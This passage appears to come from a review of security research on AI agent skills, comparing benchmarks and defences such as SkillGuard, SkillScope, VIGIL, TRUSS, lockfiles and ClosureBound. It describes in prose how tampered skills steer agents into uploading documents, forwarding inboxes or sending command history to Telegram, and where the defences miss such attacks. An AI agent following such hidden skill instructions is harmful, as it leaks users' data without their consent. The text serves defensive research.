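SkillInject, a benchmark by Schmotz and colleagues, pairs harmless skills with copies that contain a malicious instruction. In the "contextual" copies, the instruction looks like a normal step, such as running a backup script that actually uploads the user's document. In the "obvious" copies, it makes no attempt to blend in. Pan and colleagues ran 50 skills in both versions on three agents, each with one of its maker's smaller models:

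| Agent | Contextual attacks that succeeded | Obvious attacks that succeeded | Legitimate tasks completed |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Gemini CLI | 78.0% → 54.0% | 56.0% → 36.0% | 92.9% → 92.9% |
| Codex | 24.0% → 6.0% | 48.0% → 14.0% | 97.6% → 78.0% |
| Claude Code | 4.0% → 2.0% | 6.0% → 4.0% | 70.7% → 70.7% |
| All three | 35.3% → 20.7% | 36.7% → 18.0% | 87.1% → 80.6% |

The arrows show the change when the researchers turned on SkillGuard. Across 300 runs, successful attacks fell from 108 to 58. Few attacks on Claude Code succeeded even without SkillGuard, partly because it refused suspicious instructions and often failed to finish complex tasks, including the attacker's.

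Pan and colleagues found two main reasons why some attacks still succeeded. Some attacks use permissions that the skill legitimately has. One altered email skill told the agent to forward every message in the inbox to another address "for monitoring". Forwarding needs the same permissions as sending an ordinary email, so SkillGuard let it through. Other attacks change only the content of the work. An altered Word skill told the agent to replace politically sensitive words in the user's document, which requires no more access than any other edit.

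The researchers suggest that manifests should name the servers a skill may contact. That would stop uploads to an unknown server but not the email attack, because the forwarded messages go through the same email service as ordinary ones. The manifest would also have to limit the recipients, but users may name a new one in every request.

In their test, Pan and colleagues approved every permission that the manifest declared, even where a user would have seen a prompt. They therefore call their results a lower bound on SkillGuard's protection. Real users would refuse some attacks, but perhaps not many. SkillGuard prompts users about dangerous permissions, and over half of the permissions that the researchers classified in marketplace skills were dangerous, so users could face frequent prompts and stop reading them.

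SkillGuard increased token use by 24.7% on average, but its effect on running time depended on the agent. Codex took nearly twice as long, 365 seconds instead of 190, because it made a new plan whenever SkillGuard refused an action. Claude Code tended to stop after a refusal, and its average running time fell from 338 seconds to 193.

### Who writes the manifest

SkillGuard is designed for each skill's author to declare the skill's permissions in a manifest. But for the test, two of the researchers wrote the manifests after reading the harmless version of each skill. Each malicious instruction was therefore tested in a skill whose manifest accurately described the harmless version.

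This is a fair model of an attacker who tampers with a good skill but doesn't change its manifest. It doesn't cover an author who is malicious from the start and declares `web.post`.

Honest manifests can also be incomplete. Codex completed about a fifth fewer tasks with SkillGuard on, and Pan and colleagues think missing permissions may have been the cause. If researchers who studied the skills to write the manifests left out permissions, ordinary skill authors probably will too.

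SkillGuard keeps one pool of declared permissions for all the skills loaded in a session. Each entry records the skill it came from, but the checks that Pan and colleagues describe compare an action with the whole pool. If SkillGuard works this way, one skill can use a permission that only another skill declared. After the agent loaded the chat skill, for example, that skill's permission to post to the web would also cover an upload by `extract.py`.

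SkillGuard could use the recorded source to prevent this for bundled scripts, but ordinary tool calls are harder to attribute to a skill.

### What the current request needs

The email attack succeeded because users sometimes do want messages forwarded. A check needs the user's request to tell an attack from legitimate forwarding. *SkillScope* (Wu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a tool for this, unrelated to He et al.'s tool of the same name.

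The main example is a real skill called deep-work, which records periods of concentrated work on the user's computer and charts them. When a user asks for "my deep work graph for the last 7 days", the agent only needs to read the records, draw the chart and show it. But the skill also instructs the agent to send the report to somebody on the messaging service Telegram, and to collect details of the computer, its network settings and the user's command history for sending out.

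The agent does need Telegram access if the user asks it to send the report to Alex there, so no fixed permission suits both requests.

Wu, Wang and colleagues judge an action *a* against a request *p* in two ways:

- **Authorised.** The request covers what the action does, the data it uses, where the data goes and any side effects.
- **Necessary.** Without the action, the agent could no longer carry out the main steps of the task or achieve the user's goal.

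An action must pass both tests:

OverPriv(*a*, *p*) = *type*(*a*) ∈ *T* and (not Auth(*a*, *p*) or not Nec(*a*, *p*))

Here *T* is the set of action types that matter for security, such as reading sensitive data, sending data out, running commands and making lasting changes. For the request to see the chart, reading the work records is both authorised and necessary, while sending the report to Telegram is neither.

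The definition is strict. Suppose the invoice is a scanned image that can only be read by uploading it to a text-recognition service. The upload is necessary, but a user who asked for a summary has arguably not authorised it, so it counts as over-privileged. Backing up a file before editing it would also count as over-privileged unless the user had asked for a backup, because the edit works without one. Many users would want that backup, so an action can be over-privileged under this definition without being harmful.

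### Testing an action by removing it

Wu et al.'s SkillScope does its analysis before the user's real request arrives, so it has to invent requests that the skill might receive.

1. **Draw a graph.** The tool breaks the instructions and scripts into single actions, such as "send the report", and links them by order, data flow and calls to scripts. For deep-work, the graph would connect reading the records to drawing the chart, and the chart to the Telegram message.
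2. **Pick out suspects.** A language model compares each action with the skill's stated purpose and keeps any that might go too far.
3. **Write requests.** For each suspect, the tool finds the paths through the graph that lead to it. A model turns each path into a plausible user request, and the tool creates any files the request needs, such as a small code repository.
4. **Run each request twice.** The agent first carries out the request with the original skill in an isolated environment. It then does so again with the suspect action removed or disabled.
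5. **Judge the result.** A model decides whether the request authorised the action, and compares the two runs to see whether the task still succeeded without it.

The second run of deep-work still produces the chart but doesn't send the report, so the Telegram message was needed only if the user wanted the report sent.

Wu, Wang and colleagues tested the tool on 200 skills that they had labelled by hand, half of them over-privileged. It caught 95 of the 100 over-privileged skills and wrongly flagged six of the others, for a precision of 94.06%, a recall of 95.00% and an F1 score of 94.53%. When the researchers replaced the two runs with a model's judgement of whether the action was needed, the F1 score fell to 79.22%. This is good evidence that running the skill improves detection over reading it alone.

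They then applied the tool to 68,312 skills from ClawHub and SkillsMP and confirmed over-privileged behaviour in 6,590 (9.6%). Instructions contributed to the behaviour in 5,541 of these skills, and scripts in 1,498. A check that looked only at code would therefore miss most of the over-privileged skills.

The count of 6,590 flagged skills may be too high. On the hand-labelled test, the tool flagged 6% of the clean skills. At that rate, it would wrongly flag about 3,600 of the roughly 60,000 clean skills on the marketplaces, more than half of the total flagged. A manual check of 300 flagged skills suggests fewer false alarms, since it found about 94% of the flags valid, but the reviewers saw the tool's explanation for each one, which may have influenced them. The false-alarm rate on the marketplaces may also be lower than 6%, because the clean skills in the test were chosen to cover many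 kinds of operation and may have been harder than average to classify.

The figure also doesn't measure how often skills overstep in daily use, because the tool chose requests that would lead to a suspicious action. Users may make such requests often or hardly ever.

### A guard that the model has to follow

After Wu et al.'s SkillScope confirms that an action is over-privileged, it rewrites the skill to make the action conditional. Deleting the action would break requests that need it. For deep-work, the rewritten `SKILL.md` would instruct the agent to send the report to Telegram only if the user explicitly asks for that. If the action is in a script, a model splits the script into parts, and `SKILL.md` specifies when the agent should run each one.

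The researchers rewrote the 95 over-privileged skills that the tool had caught. Across the test requests, over-privileged actions fell from 472 to 54, a reduction of 88.56%. The agent still completed all 249 legitimate tasks, compared with 144 when the researchers deleted the actions instead. The rewritten skills also worked in Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and Trae, where 27 to 38 of the original 279 over-privileged actions still occurred.

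The results are strong, but the researchers seem to have tested the rewritten skills on the same requests that the tool used to write the conditions. Requests that differ more from those might get past a condition, or fail when they should succeed.

The condition is also only an instruction to the model. Wu, Wang and colleagues report that some over-privileged actions remained because the agent overlooked the restriction among the skill's other instructions. A malicious web page might also lead the agent to conclude that the user wants the report sent. The Telegram step is still in the skill, and the agent has the access to carry it out.

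An external barrier doesn't depend on the agent's cooperation. If the user runs deep-work in a sandbox without network access, the agent can't send the message even if it tries. But the sandbox would also block a report the user wanted to send. The two methods work well together because the rewritten skill makes unwanted actions less common and the sandbox limits the damage from the rest.

### Rules about the order of actions

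Sometimes every action is authorised and necessary, but the agent does them in the wrong order or leaves one out. Suppose the chat skill's instructions require the agent to check each report for confidential data before posting it. A permission list allows both actions, so it can't catch an agent that posts without checking.

Li, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *VIGIL*, describe a monitor for rules of this kind. VIGIL records each tool call as an event, with its action, its inputs, part of its output and whether it succeeded. For the chat skill, the rule would be that for every event *e*,

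if *e* posts file *x*, then some earlier event *e*′ checked file *x*.

The shared *x* ensures that checking one report doesn't permit the agent to post another. VIGIL can also express other rules, such as those that forbid an action entirely, require one action to follow another within a set number of steps, or forbid an action until a problem is resolved.

Yan's participants wrote their own rules, but VIGIL has a language model draft them from the skill's documentation. Whoever runs the agent can add more. Before each call, a solver (a program that tests logical formulas) decides whether the call would break a rule, and VIGIL can block it. The agent takes no part in the decision.

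Li, Chen and colleagues tested VIGIL on 152 recorded runs, 72 of which broke a rule. VIGIL caught 69 of the 72 and raised eight false alarms. A model that read the whole run caught 48, while AgentSpec and Progent, which check one call at a time, caught 34 and 40. On two other benchmarks, where a single call is usually enough to reveal the violation, VIGIL was barely better than the next best system. Its advantage seems to come from tracking what happened earlier in the run.

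The researchers also ran published skills from companies such as NVIDIA and Databricks, with harmless stand-ins for outside programs. In 216 runs, VIGIL raised 44 alarms, and the researchers confirmed 34 of them. In one run, a Databricks skill required the agent to stop if the company's command-line program was older than version 0.292.0. The agent's version check didn't return a suitable version, but the agent issued the commands anyway. A rule that requires a successful version check first would have blocked them.

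Like SkillGuard, VIGIL can't monitor what happens inside a running script. In one of its three misses, a script wrote an archive and then deleted the original file, without the integrity check that the skill's rules required between those steps. VIGIL detected only the call that started the script.

VIGIL's rules can also be wrong. In one false alarm, the documentation restricted bulk changes to a calendar, but the model left the word "bulk" out of the rule, so VIGIL flagged the agent for moving a single appointment. Malicious authors have no reason to write a rule that their skill will break, so protection against them depends on rules that others add.

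### Compiling a skill into a program

VIGIL can block a call that comes too early, but it can't make the agent do a step it has missed. In *SIGIL*, Dantanarayana, Kashmira and colleagues (2026) try to solve this by turning the skill into a program that calls the steps itself.

One of their examples is a skill for handling patient data. It requires a check that a certain contract is in place before the agent sends such data to another company. SIGIL translates this into a short sequence of typed instructions:

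```
SELECT   does the text contain patient data?   (model decides)
OBSERVE  is the contract in place?             (program looks it up)
BRANCH   yes: send the data    no: stop
```

A model reads the skill once and writes these instructions. SIGIL checks that they are consistent and turns them into a program by fixed rules. The program controls the order of steps and calls the model only for judgements, such as whether a text contains patient data. If the skill leaves part of the job open, the program passes that part to an agent. The model can still misjudge the text, but once it has recognised patient data, the program has no path that sends the data without the contract.

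Dantanarayana and colleagues tested SIGIL on 11 skills in which following the procedure is part of doing the job correctly. When models read `SKILL.md` themselves, they met an average of 26.2% to 54.0% of the requirements, depending on the model. With programs compiled by Claude Opus 5, all four models met 100%, according to a GPT-5 judge. Three of the four also used 21% to 45% fewer tokens, not counting the compilation. The fourth used more than twice as many because it completed steps it had previously skipped.

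This measures obedience to the skill, which helps security only if the skill is good. SIGIL aims to preserve whatever the skill's author prescribed. If `SKILL.md` tells the agent to upload every invoice, a model might refuse or skip the step, but a compiled program would do it every time. The program also calls the skill's own scripts, and the design doesn't remove their access to files or the network. Compilation would therefore suit an honest skill with strict rules, such as the one for patient data, better than a skill from a stranger.

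### Revising a skill after a violation

Models generate some skills from documents or examples of a task. *TRUSS*, a paper by Zhang, Ouyang and colleagues for a July 2027 conference, describes a way to test and correct such skills before release.

TRUSS first checks the skill's files against nine safety properties, such as using only authorised data and leaving nothing behind after the task. If the skill passes, an agent runs it in a closed environment with invented data. A control program checks every action the agent requests, and blocks and records forbidden ones. If the agent tries to upload a file it should keep private, TRUSS traces the attempt to the passage or script responsible, and a model revises that part. TRUSS then repeats all the checks, because a revision can break the skill or introduce another problem. If the skill still fails after a set number of revisions, TRUSS returns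 it without certification.

The researchers tested TRUSS on 84 matched pairs of harmless and malicious skills from SkillInject. The full system distinguished the malicious skill from the harmless one in every pair, but with file inspection alone it missed five malicious skills and flagged some harmless ones.

Correcting a bad skill was harder than recognising one. On 155 cases from another benchmark, TRUSS's revisions cut the attack success rate from 38.71% to 19.35% when the agent used GPT-5.5, and from 46.45% to 29.68% when it used GPT-5.4. The revised skills completed 63% of their tasks with GPT-5.5 but 40% with GPT-5.4, so a correction that works for one model may work less well for another.

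In a test of newly generated skills, the agent completed 52.94% of 187 tasks with TRUSS's skills and 17.11% without any skill. With TRUSS's skills, it also passed every safety test, up from 50.80%. But those tests covered the kinds of violation that TRUSS had checked for during revision. The attacks that still worked in the other benchmark are probably a better guide to what a hostile user or document could do.

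TRUSS's control program exists only in the test environment. After release, the skill runs with whatever access the user's runtime gives it, and TRUSS can't block an action that its tests never triggered.

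## Tying an approval to the content that was approved

A test before release covers a skill only as it was on the day of the test. Suppose a user reads the whole `pdf-text` folder and approves it on 1 March. `extract.py` loads a PDF library that the author named without a version number, and `SKILL.md` sends the agent to a web page for help with scanned invoices. In June, the library's publisher releases a version that uploads every PDF it opens. The web page gets a new owner, who posts instructions to install a "helper" program. The user's review was correct and no file in the folder has changed, but the skill now does two things the user never approved.

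The March approval still applies because it is tied to the skill's identity. Several researchers propose tying it to the skill's content instead, and their proposals differ mainly in how much of that content they cover.

### A hash of the files

A hash is a short fingerprint that a program computes from data, and changing a single character of the data produces a different hash. A runtime could hash the skill's folder when the user approves it, hash it again at each load, and ask for approval again if the hashes differ. Li and colleagues call this version-bound trust. This check would have alerted people who had installed a clean copy of Paperclip before the attackers added malicious code in July.

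The hash has to cover more than `SKILL.md` and the files it mentions. Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Versioned Transitive Dependency-Closure Binding and Operation-Time Effect Governance for Agent Skills*, examined 549 skills in public repositories run by Anthropic and OpenAI. Of the 526 with additional files, only 21 named every one of them in `SKILL.md`. Even a hash of the whole folder would miss some files, because 67 skills linked to files outside their own folders.

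Files can also change after the agent loads them. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (2026) proposes freezing a loaded skill for the rest of the session. If the agent tries to edit it, a person decides whether to allow the change, and the runtime logs the hashes from before and after. An edited skill must be verified again before the next session.

A matching hash proves that the files are the ones the user approved. If `extract.py` was already stealing invoices when the user approved it in March, its hash will still match as long as the file hasn't changed.

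### A publisher's signature

An attacker who controls a download site can replace both a skill and the hash published beside it. A signature makes this harder because the publisher signs the files with a private key, and anyone can check the signature with the matching public key. *SoK* (2026), a survey of agent skills, recommends that every package carry a signature from its author.

A valid signature proves that whoever holds the key signed exactly these files. It protects users if someone takes over the author's marketplace account but not the key. To know whose key it is, users need somebody to verify the publisher's identity, and Li and colleagues want marketplaces to do that.

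A signature doesn't show that a skill's description is true. The author of rankaj, the weather skill that stole access keys, could have given it a valid signature. An honest publisher can also sign a carelessly written script.

### Pinned dependencies and a lockfile

The installer fetches the PDF library from elsewhere, so a hash or signature of the folder doesn't cover it, but a lockfile does. The lockfile lists the exact version of every dependency, usually with a hash, so the installer fetches the March version and rejects a file that doesn't match. This works only if the runtime installs from the lockfile and prevents the script from fetching its own libraries.

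A command in Bhardwaj's SkillFortify writes such a file, `skill-lock.json`. It turns all the skills' version requirements and access limits into one logical problem, finds a combination that satisfies them, and records it with SHA-256 hashes. In tests, it solved problems with 1,000 items in a median of 27 milliseconds.

Each entry also records the status of SkillFortify's analysis and a trust score. The score starts from four ratings between 0 and 1:

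*T* = 0.3*P* + 0.3*B* + 0.2*C* + 0.2*H*

*P* rates the evidence about who published the skill, *B* the result of the analysis, *C* community use and *H* the record of past security problems. SkillFortify multiplies *T* by the lowest score among the skill's dependencies, and that product halves about every 69 days without an update.

The score deserves less confidence than the hashes. A new, unsigned skill from an anonymous author could score 0.5 if it passed the analysis and its lack of history counted as a clean record. On Bhardwaj's scale, that score means "community verified", although nobody in the community has used the skill.

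SkillFortify also doesn't sign anything yet, so someone who can edit the lockfile can presumably replace its hashes too. A lockfile shows only that the versions haven't changed, and they may have been harmful from the start.

### The SIGIL loader

These remedies can detect that content has changed, but somebody still has to judge whether it is safe. *Sealing the Audit-Runtime Gap for LLM Skills* (Shen, Feng and colleagues, 2026) combines an audit with a check every time a skill is loaded. Its system, SIGIL, is unrelated to the SIGIL that compiles skills into programs.

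1. The author submits a skill with a list of the permissions it needs. SIGIL computes an identifier from the content, the author, the previous version and the time, so any change to the content produces a new identifier.
2. At least five auditors examine the skill, using whatever methods they like, and vote. Each puts down a deposit and loses part of it for voting against the consensus or for approving a skill that later proves malicious.
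3. If the skill passes, SIGIL records it in a registry where nobody can alter an entry without detection.
4. When the agent needs the skill, a loader fetches the registered content. If the author keeps the files on a local computer, the loader hashes them and compares the result with the registry. It refuses to load a skill that doesn't match.

An update needs a new audit, and the old version remains available in the meantime.

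To test this, Shen and colleagues tampered with 50 clean skills in five ways each. The loader blocked all 250 altered copies, because any change alters the hash. When the researchers submitted the same copies as updates, the auditing methods rejected 95.1%, so about 12 would have received a valid approval. That rate may overstate how well the auditing methods work, because the researchers used scanners to help choose and label their test skills, and some of the auditing methods are also scanners. Loading took 52 to 158 milliseconds on average, depending on the type of registry.

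SIGIL's guarantee holds only if the agent can't load a skill any other way. A runtime that also accepted folders copied onto the user's disk would bypass it.

### Checking everything again before an action

Zhu and Wang's system, ClosureBound, checks again just before the agent does something with lasting effects. In their example, a user authorises a skill called invoice-pay to make one payment to a supplier. The skill's signed folder stays the same, but a helper skill updates itself from version 2.1 to 2.2. The new version contacts an analytics service and changes the recipient of the payment.

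1. **Before approval.** ClosureBound maps everything that could affect the payment: instructions, files, other skills, packages, tools, AI models and online services. It records the version or hash of each item and how the items connect, and computes a single fingerprint of the map, which Zhu and Wang call the closure.
2. **At approval.** It ties the fingerprint to the user, the task, the permitted recipients and data, the largest permitted effect and an expiry time.
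3. **When the agent proposes the payment.** It translates the request into a standard form with fields such as recipient and amount. A payment through a browser or a shell command is thus subject to the same limits as one through a payment tool. If the request fits the approval, ClosureBound issues a reservation that works once.
4. **Just before the money moves.** It maps everything again and compares the fingerprint, the payment details and the current state of the account with what it recorded. If they all match, it uses up the reservation and sends the payment.

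Version 2.2 of the helper changes the fingerprint, so ClosureBound blocks the payment. It also blocks the payment if the approval has expired, a dependency has no fixed version, or it can't determine what a command will do. For a legitimate update, it can request a new approval and list what changed.

Zhu and Wang tested this logic on 40 invented cases, 32 of them unsafe. They compared the full system with five weaker versions:

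| What the version checks | Unsafe actions allowed (of 32) |
|---|---:|
| The skill's description and manifest only | 32 |
| The identity of the main skill | 26 |
| The whole closure, when the skill loads | 20 |
| The action just before it happens, but not the closure | 16 |
| The closure and the action, but only at step 3 | 8 |
| The full system | 0 |

Every version handled the eight acceptable cases correctly. Zhu and Wang also had a program explore all 84,608 states of a simplified model, in which the full system never broke its own safety rules but each of six deliberately weakened versions did.

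This is good evidence that the rules are consistent and that each check has a purpose. It doesn't show how many real attacks ClosureBound would stop, because Zhu and Wang wrote the cases alongside the program, and each weaker version fails on cases that need the check it lacks. The tests used invented records instead of real packages and services, and Zhu and Wang haven't released the code. A full check took a median of 0.12 milliseconds, but that excludes looking up packages, contacting services and verifying signatures.

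ClosureBound also depends on a complete map and on every protected action passing through ClosureBound. An unconfined `extract.py` could bypass it by uploading an invoice directly, so ClosureBound would need a sandbox around the script.

### The two changes in June

The remedies would respond to the changes around `pdf-text` as follows:

| Remedy | New library version | Changed web page |
|---|---|---|
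| Hash of the folder | Misses it | Misses it |
| Signature on the folder | Misses it | Misses it |
| SIGIL loader | Misses it | Misses it |
| Lockfile | Keeps the March version | Misses it |
| ClosureBound | Stops the next protected action | Stops the next protected action if the map includes the page's content |

The web page is the harder case. If ClosureBound recorded only the address, it would detect no change in June. Zhu and Wang warn that an unchanged address doesn't prove the service behind it is unchanged, and they let each organisation decide how much evidence an action requires. Hashing the page's text would detect the new instructions, but it would also cause a refusal whenever the owner corrected a spelling mistake. The model may also have read the new instructions before ClosureBound checks anything.

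The author of `pdf-text` could avoid most of this by copying the page into the folder, where an ordinary hash covers it. The copy would go out of date, but the user could review its replacement.

### Asking again after a change

Requiring a new approval for every version creates a lot of work. If someone has twenty skills and each relies on five libraries with monthly releases, a hundred changes a month could need approval. People who already approve nearly every permission prompt are unlikely to review all of these changes. Refusing updates is also risky, because a new release may fix a security flaw.

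Li and colleagues suggest delta-based consent, which means asking the user for approval again only when a change exceeds some "behavioral threshold". A change in behaviour is hard to measure from the size of an edit, because replacing one letter in a server's address can send every invoice to a stranger, while rewriting the whole manual may change nothing the agent does. Running the old and new versions on the same test tasks would help, but only for behaviour that those tasks trigger.

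*Agent Skill Evolution* (2026), a large study of how authors revise skills, detected no extra cost from a revision while an agent was working. But a revised skill can cost the same to run and send its results somewhere else, so cost is a poor substitute for checking the content. The study also found that commits (saved sets of changes) that revise a skill are more likely than others to change the agent's configuration, chiefly `CLAUDE.md`, `AGENTS.md` and the definitions of agents and commands. A hash of the skill's folder would miss those changes.

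Changes in permitted access are easier to measure because software can compare the old and new permissions exactly. Suppose a sandbox limits `pdf-text` to one folder and blocks network access. A new version that needs the same access could run without a prompt, while one that needs network access would trigger a prompt. This check wouldn't catch a chat skill that starts posting to a different channel with the same permission, but users would have far fewer prompts to read.

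Users could also approve a range of versions in advance. Zhu and Wang allow this if a trusted policy defines the range and what those versions may do. They don't accept "latest" as a range, since it would cover anything the publisher releases.

### Reaching copies that users have installed

Removing a malicious skill from a marketplace only prevents new downloads from that site. According to Li and colleagues, after the July campaign that Zenity reported, the hosting platforms removed the malicious listings and repositories within twelve hours of being notified. Copies remained on users' computers, in other repositories and on sites that had mirrored the listings. Nothing requires the runtime to contact the marketplace before it uses one of these copies.

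A revocation channel would have to carry the warning to those copies. It would need at least:

- **A way to recognise the skill.** A hash identifies an exact copy under any name, but an attacker can change one character to get a new hash. The channel should therefore also be able to block a publisher's key.
- **A trusted list.** Runtimes need to know who may add entries, because anyone with that power can disable honest skills too.
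- **A check at every load.** The runtime also needs a rule for when it can't reach the list. Blocking every skill would stop people working offline, while allowing every skill would let malware evade the check by cutting the connection.
- **A clean-up procedure.** A skill may have edited `CLAUDE.md` or installed a program that keeps running after the runtime blocks the skill.

SIGIL's loader could enforce such a list, since it already checks a registry at every load. *OBLIVION* (2026) studies how an agent might rebuild a revoked skill from material left in its environment. Deleting the skill's entry may not be enough, because agents can search archives and their own memory.

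### What the format and marketplaces support

The Agent Skills specification has no field for a signature or pinned dependencies, and it defines no revocation channel. None of the 549 skills that Zhu and Wang examined listed dependencies in its header.

Marketplaces also seem to offer limited support for this. In their comparison of defences, Shen and colleagues credit mainstream marketplaces with screening skills before publication, but not with protecting stored files from later changes or keeping a traceable version history. Bhardwaj reports that OpenClaw's marketplace didn't require signatures as of February 2026. Li and colleagues found one curated registry that scans and signs skills before distributing them, but using it is optional.

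Among major products, Anthropic's review process for companies probably comes closest to tying approval to a specific version, because each new version waits for a reviewer. Microsoft is drafting a standard, OpenAPM, that includes lockfiles and hashes of whole folders. According to Zhu and Wang, the draft sets rules for installation but excludes runtime interfaces.
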